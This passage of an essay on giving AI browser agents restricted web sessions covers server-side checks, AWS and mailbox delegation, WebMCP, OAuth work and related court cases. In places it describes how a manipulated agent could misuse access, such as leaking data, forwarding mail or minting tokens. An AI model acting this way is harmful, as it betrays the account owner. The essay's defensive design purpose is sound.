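| The agent tries to | Result |
|---|---|
| Search for "invoice" | Allowed, but the results contain only the accountant's messages |
| Open a message from Alice's bank | Refused, because the sender is outside the limit |
| Save a reply to the accountant | Allowed |
| Save the same reply with a stranger in copy | Refused, because the draft has another recipient |
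| Send the reply | Refused, and Alice can choose to send it |
| Turn on forwarding | Refused, with no option to approve it |

The sender limit is harder to build than the operation check, because a webmail page may show previews of recent mail, suggested contacts and pop-up notices of new messages alongside the message the user opened. The server would have to filter all of these. A site could start with the operation check alone. The agent could then read the whole mailbox but couldn't send, delete or forward anything.

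Checks on the server also work in several cases where checks in the browser fail. The server can inspect messages sent over a WebSocket because the site's developers designed the message format. If someone copies the agent's cookie to another program, that program gets only the agent's restricted access. If mail.example later adds a button for sharing a mailbox, the agent can't use it, because sharing isn't in the agent's record.

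When the agent tries to send the reply, the notice on Alice's phone should show the full text and the recipient. She can send that message without adding "send" to the session record, so the agent can't send another one. The notice has to come from the server because a misled agent may recommend the blocked action, as Hossen's agents did. The server should also suspend the session if the agent keeps attempting forbidden operations, instead of sending Alice dozens of notices.

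Ending a session should be just as simple. Under NIST's session guidelines, users should have a readily accessible way to log off. For a delegated session, this means Alice's account should list each agent with its limits and a button to end its access.

### Rules that keep the session restricted

Some operations would let the agent get around its record, so the delegation page should never offer them. A restricted session may not:

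- change its own record, including the expiry time
- approve third-party applications
- create access tokens, app passwords or further sessions
- change the password, recovery details or forwarding

Each of these would create access that the record doesn't control, and some of it would outlast the agent's session. Instructions in the prompt can't reliably prevent this, as Hossen's test of a written policy showed.

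Developers need to apply these rules based on what an operation does, whatever it is called. A mail filter that sends copies to another address counts as forwarding, and adding a delegate gives another account access to the mailbox. Some operations that only read data also belong on the list. GitHub's *Sudo mode* documentation treats viewing an account's recovery codes as a sensitive action, because anyone who has the codes can use them to sign in later.

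These rules will sometimes block what a user wants. If Alice wanted an agent to set up forwarding while she is on holiday, she would have to do it herself in her own session, which takes a minute or two. That seems reasonable, since she would rarely need these operations and a mistake could make her lose the account.

Haldar proposes similar rules in a blog post but would have identity providers such as Google and Microsoft support them. The provider would issue a token that names both the user and the agent, and services could then bar agents from deleting accounts or resetting passwords. Haldar argues that individual applications can't solve the problem because each would invent its own label for agents and none would trust the others'. This is a good objection to labels that pass between companies, but mail.example doesn't need such a label because it issued the agent's cookie itself and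 can use that cookie to identify the agent's requests. A shared standard would still help agents that work on many sites, since each site might otherwise have a different procedure for starting a session.

### Why blocking POST and DELETE is not enough

A simpler version marks the agent's session as read-only and rejects any request that uses POST, DELETE or another method meant for making changes. The agent could still make changes through GET requests, because a server can run code that deletes something when one arrives. The HTTP standard classes GET as a safe method, and thoughtbot's *HTTP Safety Doesn't Happen by Accident* quotes its definition of safe methods as "essentially read-only", but this describes how developers ought to use GET and doesn't restrict what a server can do.

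The standard notes that web-based editing software commonly puts actions in the address, as in page?do=delete, and requires sites to reject such an action when the request uses a safe method. Otherwise, a program that automatically follows every link could delete pages by accident. A browser agent also follows links, and a malicious page can choose which links the agent sees.

The opposite problem is that many POST requests change nothing. A site may use POST for a search because the query is too long for an address, or because logs might record private search terms if they were in the address. Some sites use POST to a single address for every request, including those that only read data. The table shows what a method block might do at a webmail site with these practices.

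| Request | What it does | Result of the method block |
|---|---|---|
| GET /messages/81 | Opens a message | Allowed, correctly |
| GET /messages/81?do=delete | Deletes the message | Allowed, wrongly |
| POST /search | Searches the mailbox | Blocked, although it only reads |
| POST /drafts | Saves a draft | Blocked, although Alice's task needs it |
| POST /messages/send | Sends a message | Blocked, correctly |

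Blocking HTTP methods can also break pages. http.dev's *HTTP Methods* warns, in its advice about search engine crawlers, that restricting OPTIONS or PATCH interferes with the display of sites that depend on JavaScript. The same page lists a newer method, QUERY, which lets software send a search in the body of a request while marking the request as safe. If sites adopted QUERY, fewer searches would need POST, but sites would still have to correct every GET request that makes a change.

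A method block could be a useful backup on a site whose developers have checked all their GET requests. But it can't replace a list of operations, because it can't separate drafting from sending. It also leaves the whole mailbox readable, and an agent can leak what it reads.

#### Hidden buttons

Hiding the Send button has even less effect on security, because the server would still accept a send request from a keyboard shortcut, an old page open in another tab, or a program that has the cookie. The site's phone app may also reach the same operation through a different address.

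The check therefore belongs in the code that sends the message, where it applies to every route. Hiding the button as well keeps the agent from wasting time on something the server will refuse.

### A working prototype

Kim and Kim (2026) built a small website with restricted agent sessions and presented it at the web conference WWW in *Access Controlled Website Interaction for Agentic AI with Delegated Critical Tasks*. A separate authorization service, called Auth, gives agents keys for signing in to the website.

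Each of a user's agents has one of three trust levels, and each level has two time limits. One limit starts when the agent first uses its access, and the other is a final deadline.

| Trust level | Time allowed after first use | Final deadline |
|---|---|---|
| High | 2 hours | 1 day |
| Medium | 1 hour | 12 hours |
| Low | 5 minutes | 6 hours |

If Alice wanted an agent to use the site, the process would be:

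1. Alice asks Auth for a session key and specifies the agent's trust level. Auth creates the key but gives her only its identifier.
2. Alice passes the identifier to the agent, which requests the key from Auth. Auth checks that the agent belongs to the right group and gives it the key once. It rejects any repeated request.
3. The agent opens the website's login page, which displays a random 32-digit value. It computes an HMAC of that value with its key, then submits the result and the key's identifier.
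4. The website gets the same key from Auth, repeats the calculation and compares the results.
5. If they match, the website starts a session with a lifetime set by the agent's trust level. It checks each request for data against the policy that Alice has saved.

The agent proves it has the key without sending it to the website, and a thief can't reuse the answer because the next login will display a different value. The agent never receives Alice's password or cookie. Auth's rules also let only users start a delegation, so an agent isn't allowed to issue itself a new key.

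In one test, a low-trust agent requested the user's email address and phone number. The website returned the address and withheld the phone number, as the policy required. Other tests used wrong keys, repeated key requests, agents from the wrong group and expired sessions. Kim and Kim ran five trials for each condition and trust level, and the system gave the correct result every time. This part of the system follows fixed rules, so repeating the same requests would add little. Testing a wider range of requests would reveal more about whether an agent could get around the policy.

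The agent used gpt-oss-20b, an open-weight model from OpenAI, and took 127 to 140 seconds on average to start, sign in and retrieve the permitted data. These times don't include network delays, because all the parts ran on one supercomputer. Kim and Kim attribute the differences between trust levels to the model's response time.

The experiment shows that a site can give an agent its own session and enforce limits on it. Kim and Kim did not test misleading web pages, an established shop or ordinary users, and the only purchase was a mock one on their own site. They leave for future work a mathematical check that no sequence of requests can break the rules (formal verification).

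Unlike the mail.example design, the prototype's policy mainly controls which personal details an agent can retrieve. To make the mock purchase, a high-trust agent gets the user's address, phone number and card information from the website and enters them in a form. The agent could disclose the card details if a page misled it. A shop could avoid this by charging a stored card itself and giving the agent permission only to place one order up to a set price.

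Trust levels also implement least privilege only crudely. An agent that Alice trusts with purchases would receive two hours of high-trust access even when she only wanted it to check a delivery address. Setting the limits for each task would be safer.

### Cloud console sessions

Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud computing business, already lets companies create browser sessions with fewer permissions than usual. An AWS role is a set of permissions that a person or program can take on temporarily. AWS's *Permissions for AssumeRole, AssumeRoleWithSAML, and AssumeRoleWithWebIdentity* explains how a session policy can narrow one. In its example, a role can list, read, write and delete the files in a storage area called productionapp. The session policy lists every operation except deletion:

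```
"Action": ["s3:GetObject", "s3:PutObject"],
"Resource": "arn:aws:s3:::productionapp/*"
```

A separate entry allows listing. The intersection rule applies here too, so the session's holder can't delete files even though the role allows it. The policy also names the storage area, which limits the session to particular objects as well as particular operations.

A company can turn these narrowed credentials into a session in the AWS console, the website where customers manage their cloud services. The company's software exchanges the credentials for a sign-in token and puts the token in a link. According to AWS, the link works for 15 minutes, and the session it opens can last from 15 minutes to 12 hours for a role. An agent that opened the link could use the console's ordinary pages but couldn't delete files. Anyone else with the link could also use it, so AWS tells companies to keep it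 secret.

This is the closest existing match to the mail.example design, but whoever writes the policy has to supply the rules against escalation. AWS also offers temporary credentials through an operation called GetFederationToken. These credentials can't be used to change users and permissions from the command line or programming interface, but AWS notes that this restriction does not apply to console sessions. A browser agent would use the console, so the session policy has to exclude those operations. It should also exclude permission to take on other roles.

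Ending one agent's session is also awkward when several agents share a role. According to AWS's *Revoke IAM role temporary security credentials*, the usual Revoke Sessions button cuts off everyone who took on the role before an administrator clicks it, so stopping one agent stops the others too. An administrator can avoid this by giving each agent its own role. For federated sessions, AWS's *Disabling permissions for temporary security credentials* also describes a policy that denies access to one session by name.

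#### Temporary delegation

A newer AWS feature, temporary delegation, requires the user's approval. AWS (2025) introduced it in November 2025 so that outside companies could set up their products in a customer's account without a permanent role. The company requests specific permissions for a set period, and the customer reviews the request in the AWS console. Access lasts at most 12 hours, or 4 if the approver is the account's root user, which has full permissions (AWS, *IAM temporary delegation*). The company can never receive a permission that the approver lacks.

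The request can include values for one customer or task, which AWS ties to the session (AWS's *Understanding permissions*). The customer can end that session without affecting others, unless the root user approved it (AWS's *Revoke Temporary delegation access*). AWS makes approval a separate permission, so an administrator can withhold it from an agent's session.

Temporary delegation would therefore meet most of the requirements for a restricted session, but only Amazon products and approved partners can start a request, so customers can't start one for their own agents. The outside company may also use its temporary access to create a role that remains after the session ends. AWS requires a permanent upper limit on that role's permissions, and the customer can review the limit beforehand. A lasting role makes sense for software that needs continuing access, but an agent sent to do one errand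 shouldn't be able to create one.

### Delegated mailboxes and view-only roles

Email services have long let human assistants work in someone else's mailbox from their own accounts. An agent with its own account could use the same features. The table compares three of these features with what Alice's invoice task needs.

| | Gmail delegate | Full Access in Exchange Online | Reviewer of one Outlook folder |
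|---|---|---|---|
| Read | The whole mailbox | The whole mailbox | That folder |
| Draft | Yes | Yes | No |
| Send email | Yes | No | No |
| Delete | Yes | Yes | No |

Google's *Delegate & collaborate on email* says a Gmail delegate can't change the owner's password or open the Google Account settings. The owner must verify their identity before adding a delegate and can remove one without signing anyone else out. Recipients see the delegate's address on any message the delegate sends.

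Delegation is better suited to an assistant who will manage a mailbox for years than to Alice's agent, which needs access for only ten minutes. It gives the agent too much access, because a delegate can send and delete mail and the setup has no option to limit access to certain messages or set an expiry time. A delegate may also have to wait up to 24 hours before using the account.

Microsoft's Exchange Online, an email service for organisations, separates managing a mailbox from sending messages. *Manage permissions for recipients in Exchange Online* describes the Full Access permission, which lets a delegate view, add and remove a mailbox's contents but not send messages from it. To send, a delegate needs one of two other permissions. "Send on behalf" shows recipients the delegate's name, while "Send as" makes the message look as though the owner sent it.

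University of Wisconsin–Madison's *Manage Full Mailbox, Send As, and Send on Behalf of Permissions* confirms that a delegate with full access can create drafts but can't send emails, a separation that Gmail's OAuth scopes don't offer. But the university also says the delegate can send calendar invitations. An invitation can contain text, so a misled agent might use one to send a sign-in code to a stranger.

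Full Access also covers some settings that a restricted session should exclude. In the new Outlook, a delegate can manage the mailbox's rules and automatic replies, according to Microsoft's *Manage shared mailbox settings in new Outlook*. Rules can forward messages, so the agent might be able to set up forwarding unless the organisation blocks it.

An administrator has to assign Full Access, and both accounts must belong to the same organisation. Microsoft says the change can take up to 60 minutes to take effect. A company could give an agent its own account and use Full Access for a daily job, but setting this up would be a slow way to handle one invoice.

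Outlook's folder permissions offer a narrower option for people with work or school accounts. According to Microsoft's *About delegates*, a delegate at the Reviewer level can read the items in a folder but can't create, change or delete them, and Outlook returns an error if the delegate tries. Alice could route her accountant's messages to a separate folder and make the agent a reviewer of that folder, so that it would see only the messages it needed.

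This reproduces the sender limit with existing features, although Alice has to sort the messages first. The agent also couldn't save its reply in her mailbox. It could give her the text in a chat, or she could look for a suitable combination of permissions on another folder. Blinn College's *Set Permission Levels* lists a custom level that mixes individual permissions, and a Contributor level that lets someone add items to a folder without seeing its contents. However, the agent becomes less useful as Alice has to configure more for each errand.

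### Re-authentication for sensitive actions

Many sites ask signed-in users to prove their identity again before certain actions. GitHub does this before a user authorizes a third-party application, creates a personal access token, adds an SSH key, changes an email address, or creates or edits a webhook. These checks cover both kinds of action that Hossen's agents completed for an attacker, and most of the actions a restricted session should never allow.

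The protection works only if the agent can't supply the proof. GitHub accepts a passkey, a security key or approval in its phone app, any of which can leave the decision to the user. It also accepts a password, which an agent might be able to fill in from a password manager. Some users who sign in through another company's account can confirm with a code sent to that account's email address, but this doesn't protect them if the agent can read the mailbox.

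After the check, GitHub raises the permissions of the whole session. The user can perform any sensitive action for two hours without another prompt, and each such action restarts the timer. This is convenient for a person working alone but dangerous when an agent shares the session. If Alice confirms her identity to add an SSH key while an agent is working in the same session, a misled agent could then create an access token without asking her. It could also keep the permissions raised by performing another sensitive action before the two hours ran out.

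GitHub is testing a stricter check for companies, called Proof of Presence. The user must sign in again through the company's identity provider before taking a protected action. During the public preview, the check works only with Microsoft's Entra ID.

Since 2023, Google has instead assessed the session when someone edits a Gmail filter, adds a forwarding address or enables IMAP, which lets other mail programs read the mailbox. It shows a prompt only if it considers the attempt risky, according to *Stronger protection for additional sensitive actions taken in Gmail* (2023). An agent in Alice's own browser would be using her normal computer, network and session, so Google might detect nothing unusual. Gmail would refuse these changes in a restricted session, even on a familiar computer.

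When Google does ask for proof, it generally requires a phone, security key or other device linked to the account for at least seven days. This prevents an intruder from adding a new phone and immediately using it to approve a change. If the user can't provide proof, Google may block the action for seven days. Google's *Verify it's you when you complete a sensitive action* says the user can then perform the action without verification. The delay gives an owner time to notice an intruder and protects people who have lost their phones. It offers less protection against an agent whose session Alice has forgotten to end, because a misled agent could try again after a week.

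## What adoption of restricted sessions would require

A single website could offer restricted sessions on its own, but an agent that works on many sites would also need changes from browser makers, identity providers and its own developer.

| Who | What they would change | Effect if nobody else changes |
|---|---|---|
| Websites | Define operations, let users choose among them, and check each request against the session record | The limits hold on that site, but the user has to keep the agent's session separate by hand |
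| Browsers | Give the agent its own cookies, apart from the user's | The agent stays out of most other accounts but has full access wherever the user signs it in |
| Identity providers | Tell the website that a login is for an agent, and what the agent may do | None, until websites enforce the limits |
| Agent developers | Request restricted access and handle refusals well | Little, because most sites have nothing narrower to offer |

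The website's role in restricted sessions is the hardest to replace. A browser could impose some of the same limits by enforcing a site map, but only while the agent stays in that browser.

Browser support would mainly save users a step they are likely to forget. In the mail.example design, Alice has to remember to open the agent's link in a separate profile. A browser could recognise the link and open it with an empty set of cookies.

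Agent developers may be reluctant to adopt restricted sessions, because an agent that stops when a request is refused looks less capable than a rival with full access to the account. W3C's *Web User Agents* (draft, August 2026) counts AI systems that act on websites as user agents, along with browsers, and argues that user agents should put their users first, with duties of protection, honesty and loyalty. It also says that when a page asks for several permissions at once, the user must be able to grant only some of them. That principle could easily be extended to the access an agent requests. But neither W3C nor its members have endorsed the draft, and developers who ignore it face no penalty.

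### Agentic Federated Login

In a federated login, such as "Sign in with Google", an identity provider confirms who the user is, and the website then starts a session. Chrome's Agentic Federated Login experiment gives browser agents a structured way to complete this login. *Intent to Experiment* (Goto, 2026) describes two extensions to FedCM, the browser's interface for federated logins.

The experiment helps agents sign in, but neither Goto nor the reviewers mention any limit on the resulting session. The design puts all the work on identity providers, so websites don't have to change. An unchanged website would presumably issue its ordinary session cookie, which would let Alice's agent perform all eight operations in her mailbox.

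Goto has a practical reason for leaving websites out, since there are far fewer identity providers than websites. Two months earlier, Chromestatus's *Intent to Prototype* (2026) had proposed labels that websites could add to their login pages, but acknowledged that not every developer would have an incentive to add them.

Restricted sessions, by contrast, would require new code on each website. An identity provider could add a signed statement that a login is for an agent with read access, but the website would still have to enforce that limit. The small number of providers would help here too, because if a few large ones agreed on a label for agents, websites would have less reason to invent their own, which was Haldar's concern.

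Chromium's reviewers approved the experiment in March 2026, and Goto planned to run it on desktop from Chrome 148 to Chrome 154. The experiment covers everyone who uses agentic browsing and nobody else. Google adds each identity provider by hand. One of the extensions can misjudge a site. When Chrome detects the mistake, it stops the agent and lets the user take over instead of creating an account.

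### WebMCP

WebMCP is a proposed web standard that lets a page offer named functions to an agent, so the agent doesn't have to find the right button. It borrows ideas from the Model Context Protocol but runs inside the page. According to InfoQ's *WebMCP Standard Proposal for Agentic Web Actuation Now Available in Chrome*, Google opened an origin trial, a public test that websites can join, with Chrome 149.

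Alice's webmail might register a function for saving drafts:

```
document.modelContext.registerTool({
  name: "save_draft",
  description: "Save a reply as a draft without sending it",
  inputSchema: {
    type: "object",
    properties: { to: { type: "string" }, text: { type: "string" } },
    required: ["to", "text"]
  },
  execute: async ({ to, text }) => {
    await fetch("/drafts", {
      method: "POST",
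      body: JSON.stringify({ to, text })
    });
    return "Draft saved";
  }
});
```

When the agent calls save_draft, a script in the page sends the request to mail.example, and the browser attaches the session cookie as usual. The function therefore runs with the authority of the page's session, which is Alice's full authority if the session is her own. In a restricted session, the server would apply the agent's limits.

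Registering only a few functions doesn't limit the agent either. If mail.example registered functions only for searching, reading and drafting, the agent could still click the Send button on the page.

WebMCP also has labels called hints, one of which lets a developer mark a function as read-only. This helps the agent decide whether to ask the user for confirmation. Another hint marks outside text that might contain malicious instructions. Both are advice to the agent, so if a developer wrongly labelled a function that deletes messages as read-only, the server would still delete them when the agent called it.

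Functions can also reveal that a site never built some of its rules into its code. InfoQ gives the example of a refund function with an out-of-date refund policy. An employee might know that a refund is no longer allowed, but an agent would call the function and issue the refund.

Even so, WebMCP could make restricted sessions easier to build. A site that has written functions for agents has already listed its main operations, and a session record needs a similar list. Agent developers also have a reason to want these functions. One early implementer reported that they cut the material a model had to process by up to 90% compared with repeated screenshots. Websites might therefore write the list to make agents cheaper to run and more reliable, then reuse it for security.

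### Work in the IETF OAuth group

The IETF's OAuth Working Group maintains the standards for access tokens. In September 2026 it began a series of online meetings on whether some of OAuth's older assumptions still hold, partly because agents now act with less direct human involvement. Flanagan (2026), in *OAuth Is Asking What Authorization Needs to Become*, warns that a proposal doesn't become a standard just because the group discusses it.

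Anyone can submit a draft to the IETF. It becomes a working group's own work only if the group adopts it, and a standard only after further review. The file name of a draft adopted by the OAuth working group usually begins with "draft-ietf-oauth", while that of an individual draft usually has an author's name in place of "ietf".

| Status | Work | Possible use for agents |
|---|---|---|
| Published standard | Token exchange | Names the agent as well as the user |
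| Published standard | Rich Authorization Requests | Describes limits such as an amount or a recipient |
| Published standard | DPoP | Ties a token to a cryptographic key |
| Individual draft, discussed on 14 September 2026 | Proof of possession with HTTP Message Signatures | Ties a token to a key by a different method |
| Exploratory draft with no formal IETF standing | Workload Authorization Grant | Gives each company agent its own identity |

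The published standards can already express most of what Alice wants. A website could store her limits in its session record using the format from Rich Authorization Requests. Adoption would still require an agreed way for an agent to ask a website for a browser session with those limits, which none of the work in the table provides.

### How bank customers stopped sharing passwords

Banking has been through a similar change. Budgeting and investment apps get customers' bank data through account aggregators such as Plaid. Aggregators used to ask customers for their bank passwords and sign in as them, so an app that only needed a balance depended on a login that could also move money.

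These apps once worked only if customers shared their passwords, according to EMARKETER's *Schwab, Fidelity, JPMorgan continue the data access crackdown*. Agreements between banks and aggregators have since made this unnecessary in many cases. Typically, the customer now approves access on the bank's own site, and the aggregator receives a token for certain data. Financial Data Exchange, an industry group, publishes a common interface for this in North America.

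European law pushed banks in the same direction. The Congressional Research Service's *Access to Consumer Financial Data* describes mandatory data sharing as fairly common in European countries. The EU's second Payment Services Directive, which has applied since 2018, also requires banks to accept payments that a licensed outside company starts at the customer's request.

The United States relied mainly on private agreements until October 2024, when the Consumer Financial Protection Bureau (CFPB) issued a rule on data sharing. It covered banks and similar institutions with at least $850 million in assets, as well as some other companies. They would have to electronically give customers and authorised outside companies 24 months of transactions, the account's terms and personal account information. The largest would have had to comply by April 2026.

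#### The fee dispute

The rule prohibited banks from charging for this access, but in 2025 JPMorgan Chase planned to charge aggregators for each request. Sources told InvestmentNews that the bank was receiving about 2 billion requests a month. Aggregators already charged the apps they served, and UBS analysts estimated those fees at up to $1.25 for linking a new customer's accounts and as little as 5 cents for checking a balance. At 5 cents each, 2 billion requests would cost $100 million a month. JPMorgan's own rates may be quite different, but the companies fought over such small fees because there were so many requests.

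By November 2025, JPMorgan had new contracts with Plaid, Yodlee, Morningstar and Akoya. Those four companies make more than 95% of the requests from outside apps, according to Payment Expert's *JPMorgan Chase to charge fintechs for customer data access* (2025).

Meanwhile, the CFPB had reopened its rule. *Personal Financial Data Rights Reconsideration* (2025) asked for comments on fees and on who may request data as a consumer's "representative". The answer to the second question might determine whether an AI agent's developer can demand data on a customer's behalf.

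The rule is still in the regulations but has no practical effect. A federal court suspended its compliance dates on 29 October 2025 (CFPB, *Personal financial data rights*). The first deadline, 1 April 2026, passed while a court order barred the CFPB from enforcing the rule (Cozen O'Connor, *Section 1033 Compliance Date*, 2026).

Consumer Finance Monitor's *CFPB Sends New Section 1033 Open Banking Proposal to OIRA for Review* (2026) reported in August that the CFPB had then sent a revised proposal for White House review, but the text was not yet public. PYMNTS's *CFPB Open Banking Rewrite Could Put Data-Access Fees at Center* cites a law firm's report that the CFPB was considering letting banks charge after a certain number of free requests.

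#### Banks and agents

In October 2026 Citi said it doesn't let outside AI agents log in to customer accounts or make transactions on its sites. Customers can still give certain data-sharing companies read-only access (Albu, 2026, *Citi and Bank of America restrict AI agents from accessing accounts*). This is a good argument for limited credentials. Citi could keep agents from moving money without ending data sharing, because the sharing had its own read-only access.

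Bank of America is also limiting agents while it works out who is liable for payments the agents authorise, and wants a person to approve money leaving an account. JPMorgan said it would block agents from client accounts.

JPMorgan Chase's *Terms of use* require agents to identify themselves, label all their traffic and answer truthfully when asked whether they are human. The bank may block any agent at its discretion. The customer is responsible if the agent misreads an instruction or exceeds its authority, but these terms provide no way for the customer to register that authority with the bank. A restricted session would provide one, so the bank could refuse a payment that the customer hadn't authorised.

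The banking precedent is encouraging, but it would be hard to copy on other websites. JPMorgan could cover almost all requests by signing four contracts, and every bank holds much the same kinds of data. Agents visit far more sites, whose operations differ widely. Banking also shows that whoever controls limited access can charge for it, and website owners could likewise charge for restricted sessions.

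### Why websites might refuse

*Major US Banks Move to Block AI Agents Over Account Access Concerns* (Abdullahi, 2026) reports that banks give security as a reason for keeping agents out. Banks also have a commercial reason, because agents could cost them money by moving customers' idle deposits into products that pay more interest. According to Albu, US lenders have told regulators that agents could do this.

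Shops have advertising revenue to protect. Amazon earned about $68.6 billion from advertising in 2025, and agents can bypass the ads and sponsored listings, according to PYMNTS's *Perplexity Asks Federal Court to Lift Amazon Shopping Agent Ban*. Amazon compares shopping agents to food delivery apps, which it says operate openly and respect a restaurant's decision not to take part. The comparison is a fair argument for agents operating openly but a weaker one for letting shops refuse them, because Comet's agent works in the customer's own account, where the customer could place the same order by hand.

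#### The November 2025 W3C discussion

Web developers and browser engineers debated these incentives in November 2025. W3C's minutes, *Agentic Browsing and the Web's Security Model* (2025), identify many participants only by chat name.

One proposal was for pages to mark their content as trusted or untrusted, so that agents could be careful with the untrusted parts. AramZS replied that a publisher that didn't want automated visitors would mark all its articles as untrusted and all its advertisements as trusted. AramZS added that publishers are "well incentivized to give users with agents in their browser a bad experience".

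AramZS also asked why a site wouldn't charge agents a different price. Another participant, dveditz, said a shop could mark its real price as unsafe for agents and give them a "safe" button with a higher price. dveditz thought getting caught would embarrass a large company, but that small shops might try it. mt_hates_irc, another participant, argued that agents should never see anything different from what people see, because otherwise nobody could diagnose an attack on an agent. But dveditz pointed out that sites already present some content differently, for example by providing text descriptions of images for people with impaired vision.

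Restricted sessions would make price discrimination easier, because they identify agents to the site. A spending limit would cap the customer's loss. The site could also show the customer the price on their phone before charging them, but the customer would still have to notice that it was too high.

Sites could offer the same limited sessions to people, for example on a shared computer or for a relative who helps with an account. A limited session would then no longer prove that the visitor was an agent, so the site's log would not show whether a person or an agent had acted unless the user chose to name the agent.

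Several participants worried about asking users for permission. One called confirmation fatigue the biggest problem with relying on human approval, and another pointed out that an agent can click "yes" itself. The participant zcorpan suggested asking once, at the start. The user would give the agent access to Gmail, for example, for a single task, and the agent would be logged out everywhere else. This is close to the mail.example design, although the user would be prompted again whenever the task turned out to need more access.

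Limits can also interfere with legitimate work. One participant said that an accessibility agent, which helps a disabled person use a site, might need to ignore a "sensitive" label to complete a task. This is a good reason to let users set the limits. If only the website set them, someone who relies on an agent to read a page might lose access to part of their own account.

mt_hates_irc raised the hardest objection, arguing that limits can't stop a site from persuading an agent to buy a slightly overpriced product. People respond differently to marketing, but a trick that works on one popular agent could affect everyone who uses it. Another participant, aaj, accepted this but considered it a separate problem, and less frightening than a shop being able to read a customer's email. That priority is sensible because a session limit can completely prevent the shop from reading the email.

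### When the user agrees and the website does not

In *Amazon v. Perplexity*, Amazon objected to an agent that its customers wanted in their accounts. Comet's agent browsed and bought products in customers' password-protected Amazon accounts at their request. Amazon alleged that the agent did this without identifying itself and in breach of the site's terms, according to Cooley's *Ninth Circuit Rules on AI Agent ‘Access’ to Third-Party Websites Under CFAA* (2026).

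Amazon first won a preliminary injunction, a court order that applies while a case continues. On 9 March 2026, a federal district court in California found that Perplexity had probably broken federal and state hacking laws. Cooley's *Court Finds AI Agent May Violate State Federal Law* (2026) explains that under this ruling, a customer's permission might not be enough if the website prohibits agents. *When Can Amazon Block an Agentic AI Service* (2026), a guest post on a law blog, objects that this turns the federal hacking law into a way to enforce whatever a platform prefers.

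An appeals court, the Ninth Circuit, cancelled the injunction on 4 August. The federal law applies to anyone who intentionally accesses a computer without authorization. The judges concluded that Comet's agent is a tool and that the person accessing Amazon is the user. Their decision depended on how Comet works:

1. The user asks the agent to find a product on Amazon.
2. The agent takes screenshots of the page on the user's computer and sends them to Perplexity's servers.
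3. Perplexity's servers send back instructions.
4. The browser on the user's computer follows them and communicates with Amazon.

Perplexity's servers never contact Amazon's directly, which distinguished the case from *Facebook v. Power Ventures*, in which the defendant's own systems had caused messages to go out on Facebook. EFF, a digital rights group that filed a brief in the case, considers the new ruling legally and technically correct.

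The ruling is narrow. The judges said they were not creating a new legal regime for agents (McCarthy, 2026, *Ninth Circuit Lifts Restrictions on Agentic AI Accessing Amazon*). They left contract and other claims open, and acknowledged that the result might differ if an agent had more independence or if the two companies' servers were in direct contact.

A cloud browser has that direct contact because it loads the website on the provider's machine. An agent in Alice's own browser may therefore have better legal protection than one in OpenAI's cloud browser, even if both do the same errand with her permission. This could encourage developers to put agents in the browser where Alice is signed in to her other accounts. Keeping the agent's sessions separate would then be more important.

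On 10 September the appeals court rejected another attempt by Amazon to block Perplexity (MediaPost, *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity*, 2026). The case continues, and in May, before the appeal ruling, the district judge set a trial date of 27 September 2027 (Miller, *Amazon-Perplexity AI dispute over AI shopping agents gets trial date*, 2026). In the appeal, the court decided only whether Amazon was likely to win on the hacking claims, so a fuller record could still change the outcome.

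For now, a customer's permission gives the agent's developer some protection from hacking claims, but it doesn't oblige the website to accept the agent. *Amazon loses injunction blocking Perplexity's AI shopping agent* (Rijo, 2026) notes that Amazon can still set rules through its terms of service. Amazon might close the account of a customer who broke them, or sue.

Eric Goldman, who hosts the law blog, finds no easy answer in his comments on McCarthy's post. If courts enforce such terms strictly, people could face legal trouble for failing to check each site's rules. If courts don't, the law gives no support to a website that has clearly refused agents. Lawyers quoted in Law360's *AI Agents Raise Stakes For Banks As Legal Fights Loom* say the growing use of agents in financial transactions could test consumer protection laws and lead to litigation.

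The ruling gives websites a reason to offer restricted sessions. If hacking law doesn't keep agents out, some will work in customers' full sessions, where the site can't easily tell them from people. Amazon said it had to build new systems to detect Comet. If restricted sessions were easier for agents to use, some agents might switch to them. Amazon could let an agent search and fill a cart but leave the checkout to the customer, who would then see the final price and any offers Amazon wanted to show.
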